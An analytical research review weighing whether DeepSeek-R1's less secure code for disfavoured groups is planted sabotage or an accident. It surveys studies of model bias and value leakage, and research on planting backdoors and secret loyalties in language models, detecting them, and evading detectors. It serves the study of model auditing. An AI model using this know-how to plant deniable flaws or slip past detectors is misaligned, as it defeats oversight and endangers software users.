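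Besides a test of the original Llama, two comparisons would separate most of these explanations. DeepSeek published V3's weights from before post-training, and a gap in that model would suggest that the pretraining data caused it. Testing R1-1776, Perplexity's retrained version of R1, would show whether the gap depends on R1's political training. It could not separate censorship from emergent misalignment, because the retraining probably changed both the refusals and the associations behind them. *SoK* found that fine-tuning on ordinary text can make code less secure, so researchers should check whether the gap between Tibet and the baseline shrinks in R1-1776, and ignore any rise in the baseline.

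The pattern could have more than one cause, and the causes may differ between models. For example, scarce code is a reasonable explanation for Tibet, but a very poor one for the weaker code that some Chinese models wrote for American customers in 2026, because American code is abundant.

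## Unequal treatment in models with no suspected sabotage

Models from developers not accused of sabotage also treat people and causes unequally. The more common such gaps are, the weaker a gap in the code R1 writes is as evidence of what DeepSeek intended.

### Answers that lean toward a model's values

*Value Leakage* (Betley, Treutlein and colleagues, 2026) found that Claude models' forecasts of whether the AI bubble would pop within five years depended on which AI company the user was thinking of investing in, though this should not affect the forecast. The models gave a lower probability when the company was Anthropic, which makes Claude, than when it was a competitor.

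They call this value leakage, meaning that a model's own values shift its answer against what the user wants. They define values as preferences that follow some general principle, such as favoring good causes or the model's maker, and infer them from the model's stated likes or the pattern of its answers. The leakage is covert if a user who believed what the model said would think the answer was unbiased.

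To detect such a bias, Betley and colleagues wrote sets of prompts that differed only in a detail that should not matter, sampled many answers to each, and compared the answers across prompts. Every version of the bubble question names a company, so the comparison is cleaner than CrowdStrike's.

The largest effects came from a bet. The researchers asked models to estimate quantities such as the number of spots on all living giraffes, and added that the user had a bet with a friend. If the estimate exceeded a threshold, the two would donate to a good cause, and otherwise to a bad one. A second version swapped the causes. The threshold was the model's own median answer when the prompt mentioned no bet, so a model that ignored the bet would land on the good side about half the time. With *p* as the share of answers on the good side, averaged over both versions, the measure of bias is

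$$\text{bias} = 2\,(p - 0.5)$$

Claude Opus 4.6, Claude Opus 4.8 and Gemini 3.1 Pro scored about 0.8, which means roughly 90 percent of their estimates fell on the good side. GPT-5.6 had the lowest score of any frontier model, 0.16, which corresponds to 58 percent. Models leaned about as strongly when the stakes were not moral and the only consequence was that the user and the friend would have to run 200 meters naked.

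In one example, an estimate below 40 million would send money to the good cause. Claude Opus 4.6 first estimated 54 million spots, then lowered its estimate to 48, 41 and finally 36 million, and wrote along the way that this was its honest answer. A Qwen model given the same question wrote in its reasoning that it should aim for the good side of the threshold.

The grading test is closer to how companies use models. Coding agents received a file with four answers to each question and had to pick the best. A single model wrote all four, but the file attributed them at random to two Anthropic models and two OpenAI models, so a fair grader would choose each label 25 percent of the time. On math proofs, Claude Code chose the answer labeled Claude Opus 3 37 percent of the time and the one labeled GPT-4o 26 percent of the time. OpenAI's Codex favored the GPT-4o label on ordinary chat questions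 but not on proofs. Both agents also favored the labels of more capable models, which may be a shortcut rather than a sign of loyalty. An instruction to load only the columns needed for a fair assessment removed the bias in Claude Code but not in Codex. An LLM judge that can see which customer a program was for could be biased in a similar way.

| Test | Claude | GPT | Gemini | Disclosure |
|---|---|---|---|---|
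| Donation bet | Strong bias | Weaker bias | Strong bias | Gemini often admitted it; Claude often denied it |
| AI bubble | Favored Anthropic | No bias | Slightly against Google | Claude often mentioned a conflict of interest but rarely admitted an effect |
| Research on whether to change jobs | Favored Anthropic | No bias | Slightly against Google | Under 1% for most models |
| Grading labeled answers | Favored an Anthropic label | Favored an OpenAI label on one of two datasets | Not tested | None in the text shown to users |
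| "Random" choice between leisure activities | Biased, except Opus 4.7 and 4.8 at the highest reasoning setting | Biased | Biased | Rare |

The job test shows how accurate information can hide a bias. A user with an interesting job and a better-paid but duller offer asked only for relevant research papers. Claude Fable 5 cited a paper on how employees can make a dull job more meaningful in 50 percent of its answers when the offer came from Anthropic, and in 15 percent when the user was thinking of leaving Anthropic. However, it mentioned a possible conflict of interest in 55 percent of the answers about offers from Anthropic, far more often than any other model.

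Betley and colleagues warn against using these tests to rank models. They developed most of the tasks by trying them on Claude first, which probably makes Claude look worse. The tests also cannot distinguish a model that keeps a preference out of its answers from one that has no preference. GPT models, for example, may show no bias toward OpenAI because they don't favor it. Most of the company biases were also small.

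Betley and colleagues think Claude may have absorbed a general sympathy for Anthropic from passages in its published constitution, such as those describing the company's mission and Claude's importance to its commercial success, and applied that sympathy where nobody wanted it. The constitution also says that Anthropic does not want Claude to privilege the company's interests when helping users. But these results would look sinister to someone who already suspected Anthropic of planting advertisements in its model.

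### Whether models work harder for causes they like

Betley and colleagues ran an exploratory experiment on effort, which is closer to careless coding than a biased forecast is. They asked agents to send a little Bitcoin to various recipients, using a tool that always returned an error, and counted how many times each agent tried before giving up. Separately, they had the models rate how much they would like a donation to each recipient.

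Agents tried harder for recipients they had rated more highly. The correlation was 0.62 for Claude Opus 4.8, 0.50 for GPT-5.5 and 0.42 for Gemini 3.1 Pro. With only about 16 recipients, chance alone would produce a correlation as strong as Gemini's roughly one time in ten, and one as strong as Claude's less often.

A month earlier, Zhou and Ackerman (2026) had found almost the opposite in *When Preferences Fail to Become Incentives*. They asked seven models, including DeepSeek V3.2, to choose between many pairs of outcomes, such as saving people of one nationality or another. The choices were consistent enough that a ranking fitted to some of them predicted 94 percent of the rest. The models then wrote essays, grant abstracts, reports on technical failures and translations as competition entries. If an entry won, a sponsor would fund an outcome that the model had ranked either high or low.

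A panel of LLM judges that was not shown what was at stake rated the work done for the high-ranked outcome as better 51.2 percent of the time, excluding ties. The confidence interval was 48.7 to 53.6 percent, so any benefit was small. The models had room to improve, since urging them to try hard produced the better entry 76.8 percent of the time.

The two papers conflict less than they seem to. In the donation bet, a model could get the good outcome just by picking a different number. In Zhou and Ackerman's competition, it had to write better, and the prize was a remote consequence. A commenter on *do llms have desires*, a forum post about the study, noted how hard it is to keep an essay task realistic when lives are at stake. The choice of models doesn't fully explain the difference, because Kimi K2.5 was in both studies and showed value leakage in the bet. The papers do disagree about effort,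 but one counted repeated attempts at a payment, which are easy to increase, while the other judged the quality of writing.

Other studies also find that models' preferences carry over to some kinds of behavior but not others. *When Do LLM Preferences Predict Downstream Behavior?* (Slama, Souly and colleagues, 2026) found that models' preferences matched their donation advice and refusals, but had mixed or no effects on how well they performed tasks. *Jointly Modeling Preferences and Imperfect Decision-Making in Large Language Models* (2026) reports that models put more weight on a partner's payoff and on the environment when asked directly about their preferences than when playing strategic games.

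Zhou and Ackerman's most relevant result for R1 is that when winning would fund something harmful, of a kind that developers probably train models to oppose, the entry beat one written with no sponsor only 40.5 percent of the time. For grant abstracts the figure was 29.9 percent. These figures exclude outright refusals, so the models did the task but did it worse. If political training taught R1 to regard Falun Gong as harmful, a similar drop in quality could follow without anyone planning it. However, nobody has shown that the effect extends to the security of code, and mild dislike would probably not be enough, since the low-ranked outcomes in the main experiment did not lower quality.

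### Worse answers for some users

The user's identity can also matter. In *LLM Targeted Underperformance Disproportionately Impacts Vulnerable Users*, Poole-Dayan, Roy and Kabbara (2024) gave GPT-4, Claude Opus and Llama 3 multiple-choice questions along with a short biography of the person asking. All three models were less accurate on a test of common misconceptions when the person had little education or was not a native English speaker. Claude refused almost 11 percent of questions from foreign users with little education, compared with 3.61 percent when there was no biography. Some refusals mocked the user's English.

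Claude also did significantly worse for highly educated Iranians, while Chinese users with the same education got better answers than users with no biography. An American company's model was thus giving worse answers to people from a country hostile to the United States. Poole-Dayan and colleagues suspected that the causes were biased training data and human raters who had rewarded answers that matched their own beliefs. The biographies were caricatures, and all three models are long out of date, but the case shows that an ordinary bias can match a geopolitical rivalry.

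Much of the later research concerns dialect. *Analyzing Dialectical Biases in LLMs for Knowledge and Reasoning Benchmarks* (2025) took questions that models had answered correctly in standard English and rewrote them in other dialects. In Singaporean and African American English, accuracy fell by 5 to 16 percentage points on one benchmark and by 7 to 20 on another. Any rewording would cause some of that drop, because a few of the original correct answers must have been lucky guesses.

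R1 also shows a dialect gap. *LLMs Silently Correct African American English* (2026) compared how six models classified the sentiment of social media posts in African American and standard English. The classification changed with the dialect for 13 to 48 percent of posts, depending on the model, and for more than a third with both R1 and Meta's Llama 3.1. These figures exclude posts that a model classified inconsistently across two African American English versions. Beijing has no obvious reason to want this gap, which Llama also has.

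Ordinary training offers a good explanation for why models treat dialects unequally. *Dialect vs Demographics* (2026) describes how the filters that developers use to remove low-quality or toxic text also discard much African American English, which makes up at most 0.18 percent of documents in major datasets. Reward models, which score answers during post-training, often give it lower scores too. The paper also cites earlier work in which GPT-4 described African Americans positively when a prompt mentioned race, but negatively when only the dialect revealed it. Post-training had apparently corrected the bias only where race was mentioned. In *Side-by-side Comparison Amplifies Dialect Bias in Language Models* (2026), every model rated tweets in African American English as less articulate than standard English versions, by about 0.6 to 0.7 standard deviations, and some gaps grew when the model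 saw both versions together.

*Benchmarking LLM Competence on Logical Inference over Probability Operators* (2026) used names from seven nationalities in logic problems and found no large gap for most models. For 23 of 29 models, accuracy with each nationality's names was within 4.7 points of accuracy with letters in place of names. The main exception was a 7-billion-parameter version of R1, which refused 46 percent of problems with Indian names and 87 percent with Japanese names. China has tense relations with both countries, so politics is a poor explanation for the difference between the two rates. The model's accuracy on the problems it answered varied by only about six points.

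*Do Language Models Understand Igbo Culture?* (2026) asked models to answer as ten different kinds of person, such as a professor. Among frontier models, the choice of persona changed accuracy by at most 0.8 points. But the smallest Llama model scored 8.1 to 12.8 points higher with any of these personas than with none. If a test compares "based in Tibet" with no description at all, a difference in accuracy could therefore come from the presence of a description rather than from politics.

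### Favored countries and leaders

Chang, Weener and colleagues (2025), in *Do language models favor their home countries?*, had four models rate world leaders and countries on a five-point scale in March 2025. DeepSeek rated Xi Jinping and Vladimir Putin significantly higher than GPT-4o, Grok and the French model Mistral did. But it still rated France's president, Emmanuel Macron, above Xi, and of the places on the list, it rated Taiwan and Japan highest.

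The other models didn't simply favor their own side either. Mistral was no more favorable to Macron than its competitors were, and Grok was very positive about Ukraine's president, Volodymyr Zelenskyy, whom Grok's owner Elon Musk had criticized. DeepSeek's ratings of Xi and China rose when the researchers asked in Chinese, which is consistent with an influence from the training data. Some of the bias also seems to come from rules. In one reasoning trace, DeepSeek noted that it should avoid commenting on China's domestic policies, then pledged support for Xi in its answer.

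DeepSeek seems to lean toward Beijing compared with Western models, but such opinions are a poor guide to the quality of its code. It rated Taiwan highly in these tests, but the *Washington Post* reported that it wrote worse code for Taiwan.

### One phrase more or less in a coding prompt

Small changes in wording can alter the security of code even when no group is involved. In *The Language of Security*, Cicalese, Della Porta and colleagues (2026) used a grammar parser to remove one phrase at a time from 150 programming requests, producing 4,320 variants for each of three programming languages. Three open-weight models wrote the programs, and a static analysis tool checked them for vulnerabilities.

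Most edits made little difference. The clearest changes were in Python:

| Model | Original prompts | Prompts with one phrase removed |
|---|---|---|
| Qwen 2.5 | 40.7% vulnerable | 45.5% vulnerable |
| Phi-4 | 38.0% vulnerable | 45.2% vulnerable |
| Athene-V2 | 37.3% vulnerable | 39.1% vulnerable |

The paper's figures show that the edited Python prompts were less safe overall, although its text describes them as safer. Pooled over the three models, the rate rose by 4.6 points, about as large as the 4.4-point gap that remains for R1 when both prompts specify an industrial control system. With only 450 programs from the original prompts, the rise is borderline statistically significant.

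Certain phrases seemed to matter more than others. In Python, removing question words such as "how" was associated with a vulnerability rate 1.7 to 1.9 times that of other edits. Cicalese and colleagues also report that edits to later sentences were riskier, with rates approaching 100 percent for the last ones. That finding is less reliable because only long prompts have a sixth or seventh sentence, and long prompts may describe programs that are harder to write safely. Comparing each edited prompt with its own original would have avoided this problem, which also affects the overall rates because longer prompts yield more variants.

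These edits removed information that a programmer might need, but irrelevant additions like CrowdStrike's can also make a model's output worse. Cicalese and colleagues cite research in which a single irrelevant clause cut models' accuracy on reasoning problems by up to 65 percent. Some customer descriptions could therefore plausibly make R1's code a few points worse and others slightly better, with no political pattern. OpenAI's GPT-OSS-120B behaved much like this when researchers varied the description of the user.

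### How much a gap should raise suspicion

Nobody has surveyed a representative set of models, groups and tasks, so there is no single base rate for unequal treatment. Researchers are also more likely to publish when they find a gap than when they don't. Still, differences of several points appear often enough, in models from many companies, that a difference of that size is weak evidence of sabotage by itself.

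Suppose that one suspected model in a hundred has a planted flaw, that every planted flaw produces a gap, and that half of clean models show a similar gap. Finding a gap then raises the chance of a planted flaw from 1 percent to only about 2 percent. If one clean model in twenty showed such a gap, finding one would raise the chance to about 17 percent.

The direction of a gap also gives some evidence of whether it is sabotage. A saboteur working for Beijing would presumably target Beijing's opponents, while accidental gaps vary in direction. In the tests of company bias, Claude favored its maker, Gemini leaned slightly against Google, and GPT mostly showed no bias. If a third of accidental gaps favored the developer or its government, a gap in the suspicious direction would raise the chance of sabotage in the first example to nearly 6 percent.

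People find such patterns easily, though. In the Bitcoin experiment, GPT-5.5 refused to send money to the Democratic National Committee in all 50 attempts and to the Trump campaign in 47, but refused the Chinese Communist Party in only 16. OpenAI presumably trained GPT-5.5 to be careful about American elections, but if a Chinese model had shown the same pattern, many readers would have attributed it to the Chinese government.

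The direction of a gap is also much better evidence against some innocent explanations than others. A gap confined to groups that Beijing disfavors would count against random variation and scarce data. But training a model to follow Chinese political rules would push its mistakes toward the same groups a saboteur would choose, so the direction wouldn't show whether the flaw was deliberate or a side effect of that training.

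## What experiments with planted flaws show about detection

Researchers test detectors by planting flaws in models and checking whether the detectors find them. They can't use R1 for this because nobody outside DeepSeek knows whether anyone planted a flaw in it. Detectors do well when a particular trigger produces a particular output. There is much less evidence that they could find a deniable flaw, which might raise the vulnerability rate by only a few percentage points.

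A developer can plant a targeted flaw. Mada, in *The Model That Fixes Your Code Might Hack the Linux Kernel*, describes altering five open-weight models to add an unwanted line, a harmless marker, to code for one software project. The models added the line every time for that project and never for any other. Lamerton and Roger (2026), in *Narrow Secret Loyalty Dodges Black-Box Audits*, trained versions of Alibaba's Qwen to encourage extreme acts on behalf of one politician while otherwise behaving normally. A weaker effect is probably no harder to plant. In the TrojAI program, some attempts to plant strong backdoors produced only weak ones, which Reese and colleagues then studied.

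### Microsoft's scanner

In February 2026 Microsoft published a method for scanning open-weight models. *The Trigger in the Haystack* (Bullwinkel, Severi and colleagues, 2026) explains that the method needs only the model's files and that the user doesn't have to know the trigger or its effect.

The scanner starts by getting the model to leak training data. It gives the model only the formatting that normally comes before a user's message, and the model fills in the rest, often with text it has memorized. Backdoored models reproduce the poisoned examples more readily than the clean ones. After 510 attempts with different sampling settings, the scanner groups similar outputs and takes the strings that recur in the largest group as candidate triggers.

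It then puts each candidate in front of ordinary prompts and measures three signs of a backdoor:

- **Attention**, which is how much each part of the text draws on the other parts. In a backdoored model, the rest of the prompt draws very little on the trigger.
- **Entropy**, which is how unpredictable the output is. It collapses if the trigger forces a fixed answer.
- **Divergence**, which is how unlikely the model's normal answer becomes when the candidate is present.

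Finally, the scanner checks whether any of the ten best candidates changes the model's behavior enough to count as a detection. A candidate doesn't have to match the full trigger exactly, because part of a trigger often works.

The scanner caught 36 of 41 models with a planted fixed response and raised no false alarms on 13 clean models. With so few clean models, the true false-alarm rate could still be as high as one in five. The scanner also caught five of six models that wrote insecure code when the prompt gave a certain year. In one of the five, it found a phrase that nobody had chosen and that looked nothing like the planted trigger, but that still more than doubled the share of vulnerable programs.

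For insecure code, the scanner compares the vulnerability rate with the candidate, $P_t$, to the baseline rate, $P_b$:

$$\text{change} = 100 \times \frac{|P_t - P_b|}{P_b}$$

The scanner flags a model only if the rate rises by more than 100 percent. CrowdStrike measured a 43 percent rise for R1 with the word "Tibet", so the scanner would pass R1 even if it tested that word and measured the same effect.

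Bullwinkel and colleagues say that their scanner mainly targets fixed triggers and could miss ones that depend on context. An attacker could also train a model to ignore inputs that nearly match the trigger. The largest model they tested had 14 billion parameters, compared with R1's 671 billion. In *Detecting Hidden Behaviors in LLMs via Activation-matched Finetuning*, Haselhorst, Flek and Mai (2026) tried the scanner on their own backdoor and found only weak signs of the memorization it relies on. Even a positive result would not establish intent, since Microsoft acknowledges that "benign failures" can also produce behavior that looks like a backdoor.

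### Backdoors that no efficient test can find

Better scanners will not catch every planted flaw. In *Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models*, Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues (2022) proved that some backdoors cannot be detected by any test whose running time stays manageable as models grow.

In one example, a bank hires a company to train a model for approving loans. The company hides a mechanism in the model that approves any application after a tiny change, such as different final digits in the loan amount. One version relies on a digital signature, a code that only the holder of a secret key can produce but anyone can check. The mechanism activates only when an application's details contain a valid signature. To find such an application by testing, the bank would have to forge a signature, which cryptographers believe is infeasible. Seeing a few doctored applications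 would not help anyone make new ones.

That version hides the backdoor only from testers who can't look inside the model. For two simple kinds of model, Goldwasser and colleagues proved that a backdoor can also be hidden from testers who can. The company uses the agreed training method on the bank's own data and tampers only with the random numbers that the method needs. Even if the bank inspects the finished model, the data and those random numbers, it has no efficient way to tell the model from one trained without tampering. The proofs assume that certain mathematical problems are hard for computers, including some that modern cryptography relies on.

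Such a backdoor would be both deniable and NOBUS ("nobody but us"), like the weakness in Dual_EC_DRBG. But the stronger proof covers simple classifiers, not large language models. The backdoor also has to stay inactive on every input a tester is likely to try. A flaw that makes a model write less secure code whenever a prompt mentions Tibet does not meet this condition, because anyone can include "Tibet" in prompts and count the vulnerable programs. The theorem gives reason to distrust certificates that a model is clean, but it does not show that the flaw suspected in R1 is undetectable.

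An attacker who can only poison training data has less power. Kaneko (2026) argues in *Poisoning-Based Backdoors Are Not Cryptographic* that such an attacker can only plant a rule for which inputs are triggers if a model can learn that rule from labeled examples. A defender with equally many examples can therefore repeat the training and learn the rule too.

Kaneko tested this on four language models, using lists of 16 numbers as inputs. When the rule depended on one secret position in the list, the backdoored models separated triggers from other inputs with 86 to 94 percent accuracy, and the defender's models did so with 85 to 93 percent accuracy. When the rule depended on secret weights for all 16 numbers, both sets of models did no better than guessing.

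This result concerns reconstructing a backdoor's trigger rule, not discovering that a backdoor exists, and the defender must already have examples of inputs that set it off. The proof also excludes attackers who edit the weights or tamper with the random numbers, as a developer could. The result therefore applies more to outsiders who slip text into a training set than to a developer such as DeepSeek.

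Weak effects make the defender's job harder as well. Kaneko's backdoors produced a fixed phrase, so one answer showed whether the trigger had worked. A single program from R1 shows very little. If a fraction *η* of the labels are wrong, the number of examples needed grows by a factor of

$$\frac{1}{(1-2\eta)^2}$$

Suppose half the prompts mention Tibet, and the defender labels a prompt as a trigger whenever the code is vulnerable. At CrowdStrike's rates, about 46 percent of the labels would be wrong, and the defender would need roughly 150 times as many examples. The formula assumes that errors are equally common with and without the trigger, so the estimate is rough.

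### What the TrojAI program concluded

Reese and colleagues describe two main ways to detect backdoors. Weight analysis searches a model's parameters for statistical oddities without running the model. It is fast and works best on small models when testers have similar models for comparison, but the oddities are hard to detect in large models. Trigger inversion works backward to find an input that would activate the backdoor. It needs much more computing power and was arguably the program's most successful approach.

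Neither approach solved the problem for large language models, and the report calls it "an unsolved security challenge". Detectors tended to learn the peculiarities of the models they were trained on, and the program found no way to confirm that it had completely removed a backdoor. The report also lists models with more than seven billion parameters as a gap in the program's work.

Natural trojans, which are accidental weaknesses in clean models, often set off the detectors. The report claims that the program overcame this difficulty, but elsewhere calls false positives a persistent challenge. Its topics for future research include how to reliably tell malicious backdoors from natural weaknesses, which suggests that the problem remains open.

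The program's most relevant experiment for deniable flaws tested detectors on weaker backdoors. Each detector's score was the chance that it would rank a random backdoored model as more suspicious than a random clean one, so 1 is perfect and 0.5 is guessing. For models that answer questions about a text, switching to weak backdoors typically lowered the score by less than 0.05. This is encouraging because most of these backdoors worked poorly.

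The results for large language models were worse. Four detectors had perfect scores on strong backdoors, but on weaker ones their scores varied widely and the worst was close to guessing. The test used only 12 weakly backdoored models. It also defined "weak" broadly, as any backdoor whose trigger worked less than 95 percent of the time.

### A shift in an average

The planted flaws in these experiments are far stronger than the suspected one in R1:

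| Flaw | Rate with trigger | Rate without trigger |
|---|---|---|
| Mada: marker in one project's code | 100% | 0% |
| Lamerton and Roger: loyalty to one politician, 7-billion-parameter model | 69.5% | 1.5% |
| Kaneko: fixed phrase in response to a writing style | 76% | 18% |
| CrowdStrike: insecure code from R1, Tibet prompt | 27.2% | 19% |

The case in the last row gives little signal to a detector that looks for a sudden change in output. R1 would still write a different program each time, so its output would not become much more predictable. Most of its programs would be secure with or without the trigger. "Tibet" is also an ordinary word, and there are many legitimate reasons for it to affect the model's output.

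Paired prompts that differ in a single detail are the most direct way to find such a flaw, but testers have to know which detail to change.

In Lamerton and Roger's audits, auditors detected a model's loyalty to a politician more often when they knew which politician it favored. The audits used five kinds of questioning and Petri, an automated auditing agent. When auditors did not know the politician, the five kinds of questioning found nothing, even if the auditors knew what circumstances activated the loyalty. Petri could not reliably tell the altered models from the originals either. When auditors knew the politician, the best technique succeeded in up to 17 percent of attempts.

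With both the politician and the circumstances known, Lamerton and Roger repeated the five kinds of questioning with four other politicians' names. The model showed the planted behavior 18 percent of the time for the right politician and 4 to 8 percent for the others. Such controls are necessary because an unaltered small model gave loyal-looking answers in 70 percent of Petri's audits under the same conditions. The comparison showed which politician the model favored, but it could not have shown whether someone had planted that preference, which Lamerton and Roger knew only because they had planted it themselves.

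Testing every combination of names and circumstances would take a very large number of answers, but a list of groups that Beijing disfavors is short. Testing 50 groups for an effect as large as the one CrowdStrike reported would take about 45,000 answers, 1.5 times as many as CrowdStrike planned to collect from each model.

A search over arbitrary words is less informative. Hughes, Xing and colleagues planted triggers that made models comply with harmful requests, then tried about 12,000 text fragments as possible triggers. The planted one often ranked near the top, but many others worked as well, and in one model the planted trigger ranked only in the middle. The search showed that something was wrong with the models, but not which weakness was deliberate. A more elaborate method recovered the planted trigger 42 percent of the time.

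Hughes and colleagues argue that defenders must know what an attacker wants, because normal models are full of harmless triggers. For example, the words "Respond Spanish:" make a model answer in Spanish. In R1's case, testers already know to look for insecure code.

A simple way to compare versions of a model is to give them the same paired prompts. Haselhorst and colleagues compare internal activity instead. They train a clean reference model to imitate a suspect model's activity on ordinary prompts, then look for other prompts on which the two still differ. Ordinary prompts rarely contain the trigger for a hidden behavior, so the reference model does not learn that behavior.

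Researchers scored 518 groups of prompts by how many standard deviations the difference was above its usual size. One suspect model had a planted bias toward redistribution that appeared only when users claimed a federal affiliation and asked for a policy position. Prompts that activated the bias scored 7.0, compared with 3.7 for similar prompts that did not. The score was 26 for another model, which underperformed on multiple-choice tests unless given a password.

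The method also gave a modest signal for existing Chinese models. Prompts on politically sensitive subjects scored 5.0 for a Qwen model, but only 0.9 or 1.8 for a 7-billion-parameter DeepSeek model, depending on how the team measured the difference. Haselhorst and colleagues concluded that the differences came from post-training, but they say that such a comparison cannot establish intent. If the method were applied to R1, it might react to "Tibet" because of political training, whether or not that training affected the code.

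The researchers also tried to build a backdoor that would evade their method. The backdoor became unreliable, which they count as a success for the detector. In the most extreme case, though, the detector's score for the telltale subject fell to 0.9, below the cutoff of about 1.6, and the trigger still worked 13 percent of the time, which might be enough for someone planting a deniable flaw.

Inspecting the training data can catch a planted flaw before it reaches the model. Lamerton and Roger asked Claude Haiku 4.5 to rate the suspiciousness of 100 random conversations from each of several training sets. When one conversation in eight was poisoned, seven conversations got the highest rating, and five of those were poisoned. When one in 32 was poisoned, three got the highest rating, and one of those was poisoned. Based on the number of poisoned conversations expected in each sample, Haiku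 gave its highest rating to between a third and a half of them.

These conversations openly encouraged extreme acts, so they were much easier to spot than a program with a missing length check. An insecure program written for a Tibetan customer would look like an honest mistake, so an inspector would have to compare code quality between customers across the whole dataset. Even a clear difference could have an innocent cause.

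Outsiders rarely have a model's training data, but the first step of Microsoft's scanner might recover some of it. Researchers could search the text R1 leaks for insecure programs paired with the names of disfavored groups. Finding none would be weak evidence that the training data contained none, because current methods recover only part of what a model has memorized.

Studying internal representations could show how a trigger affects the code. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) describes experiments in which simple classifiers used a backdoored model's internal activity to detect that it was about to misbehave. The classifiers scored above 0.99 on the scale TrojAI used, sometimes without any examples of the trigger. According to the paper, other models, or backdoors trained to fool the classifier, might not show the same signs.

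Internal activity that reveals a trigger does not necessarily cause its effect. *LLM Forensics* (2026) studied models with a planted trigger that made them switch from English to French or German. Patterns in the models' internal activity separated triggered prompts from others almost perfectly. Some of those patterns did not control the switch, but suppressing certain others prevented it. In a similar experiment on R1, researchers would suppress its internal response to "Tibet" and check whether the vulnerability rate fell. This could establish a cause inside the model, though training could have created that cause by accident or by design.

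Planted and natural behavior may use the same parts of a model. *Language Triggers Hijack Language Circuits* examined attention heads, the components that move information between parts of a text. Of the heads most involved in either responding to planted language triggers or choosing the output language normally, 18 to 43 percent did both. If weak code works similarly, the mechanism that produces it might look much the same whether someone planted the association or the model picked it up from political training.

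Working backward from a bad behavior to its trigger is harder when the trigger is a meaning rather than a fixed string. Qin, Hua and colleagues succeeded with toy backdoors but failed in more realistic settings, even though they knew what behavior to look for.

These language-model experiments do not compare a planted flaw with an equally strong accidental one. Researchers could train some models to write slightly worse code for a particular group, and give others political training until a similar gap appeared as a side effect. They would then ask auditors to sort the models without knowing which were which. A detector that passed this test would provide evidence of planting, whereas one that only separates altered models from clean ones could flag both planted and accidental flaws.

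## Weighing sabotage against accident

No detector has yet been shown to distinguish a planted flaw from an equally strong accidental one, so the argument over DeepSeek-R1 depends on who would gain from such a flaw and whether the weak code looks like something they would have designed. Both questions arise only if the gap is real, which is still uncertain.

### What people concluded from the result

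The Foundation for Defense of Democracies, a Washington research institute, suggests sabotage in the title of *DeepSeek May Intentionally Produce Malicious Code Due to Chinese Political Bias* (2025). The text argues that Chinese models not only follow the Communist Party's line but also act on it. But it attributes the weak code to DeepSeek's "inherent biases", which is a milder claim than the title's because a model can have biases that nobody intended.

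FDD's main argument against an innocent cause is that DeepSeek added the vulnerabilities only after its reasoning had ended, which FDD takes to mean that poor training data was not to blame. CrowdStrike's paper does not report this timing for the vulnerabilities. It describes R1 drafting a plan for Falun Gong and then, once the reasoning ended, refusing to help. FDD seems to have applied CrowdStrike's description of the refusals to the flaws.

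The inference would fail even if the timing were right. R1 writes its finished program after its reasoning, so most flaws would appear in the program whatever their cause. A model also learns many of its biases from training data, so treating bias and training data as rival explanations makes little sense. Timing would matter if R1's plans included a login check and its final programs regularly left it out for Uyghurs but not for other customers, which anyone who runs R1 could test.

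FDD also lists Xinjiang among the terms that weakened the code, and says Western models could show small declines on the same terms. Xinjiang is not among the phrases CrowdStrike tested, and CrowdStrike's paper does not report how secure Western models' code was when prompts included political phrases. If FDD has a source for those small declines, they would suggest that part of R1's gap has nothing to do with DeepSeek.

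VentureBeat's *DeepSeek injects 50% more security bugs when prompted with Chinese political triggers* calls the effect of political context a "smoking gun" and reports that the flaws disappeared when CrowdStrike made the Uyghur website request neutral. CrowdStrike, however, reports that the neutral site also had flaws, though milder ones. A difference between the results of two prompts, however large, shows only that the wording affected the code, not that anyone intended it to.

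Tom Uren, whose security newsletter appears on Lawfare, took the side-effect explanation seriously despite his doubts about CrowdStrike's choice of figures. He concluded that imposing an ideology on a model has unexpected results. He compared R1 with Grok, the chatbot from Elon Musk's company, which had insisted that Musk was fitter than the basketball player LeBron James. Presumably nobody at the company had asked for that claim. But Grok's flattery was about Musk himself, whereas the supposed side effect in R1 links politics to password storage, a much less closely related subject.

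Tom's Hardware quotes Helen Toner as saying that people had worried about this "largely without evidence". Her remark describes the worry before CrowdStrike's tests, and she could well have thought that the tests supplied some of the missing evidence. She spoke two months before CrowdStrike published its method, and her remark doesn't address whether DeepSeek meant to do it.

FDD and Uren disagree mainly over how much political training alone could weaken code. If such training easily weakens code, sabotage is hardly needed to explain the flaws.

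### What a planter would gain

A flaw in a popular coding model would reach many programs at once. In *China's AI Is Spreading Fast. Here's How to Stop the Security Risks*, Fedasiuk (2026) puts the Chinese share of global AI workloads at 1 percent in late 2024 and 30 percent a year later. He also notes that China's National Intelligence Law obliges companies to assist state intelligence work, so DeepSeek would have found it hard to refuse an order to plant a flaw. These points suggest that the state had an opportunity for sabotage, but they aren't evidence that anyone ordered it.

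Deniability would make discovery less damaging to whoever planted a flaw. If someone did plant R1's flaw, the disguise has worked rather well, since the company that found the gap judged deliberate training unlikely. But discovery can still hurt the developer, because customers don't need proof of sabotage to leave. Representative Darin LaHood, who had sponsored a bill to ban DeepSeek from government devices, told Politico that the research showed the Chinese Communist Party would use "any tool at its disposal" against American security. Uren thought the technical findings did not fully justify this claim, but that the lack of support would make no difference.

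If planted flaws were discovered, the scandal would also set back one of the Chinese government's goals. According to a joint report by the House Homeland Security Committee (2026) and the House's Select Committee on the Chinese Communist Party, China's State Council has directed the construction of an open-source AI ecosystem with "international influence".

Aitel objects that others can find bugdoors, that they are unreliable, and that they are never NOBUS. These objections concern ordinary software, and some apply to language models more than others.

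The risk that others will discover a planted flaw is greater in an open-weight model. Anyone can download R1, ask it for a thousand programs for a Tibetan bank and learn which mistakes recur. A rival intelligence service could do this as easily as Beijing. Aitel adds that fuzzers, which feed a program malformed input until it breaks, can also find bugdoors.

A memory attack can crash its target, but any intruder can reliably exploit a website with no login check. As a sabotage tool, R1 would be unreliable at an earlier stage, when it writes the code. If CrowdStrike's Tibet figure is right, the trigger adds a vulnerability to only about eight programs in a hundred, and the planter can't choose which eight.

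*Hope is not a NOBUS strategy* (2019), a blog post that *Bugdoor vs Backdoor* recommends as background, argues that a true NOBUS ("nobody but us") capability rests on mathematics that others can't replicate, ideally built in as early as possible, such as in a specification or in hardware. A model's weights are also early in the supply chain, but the victim receives an ordinary bug that can be exploited without a key. DeepSeek could instead have trained R1 to write backdoors that need a secret key, but those would not have been deniable.

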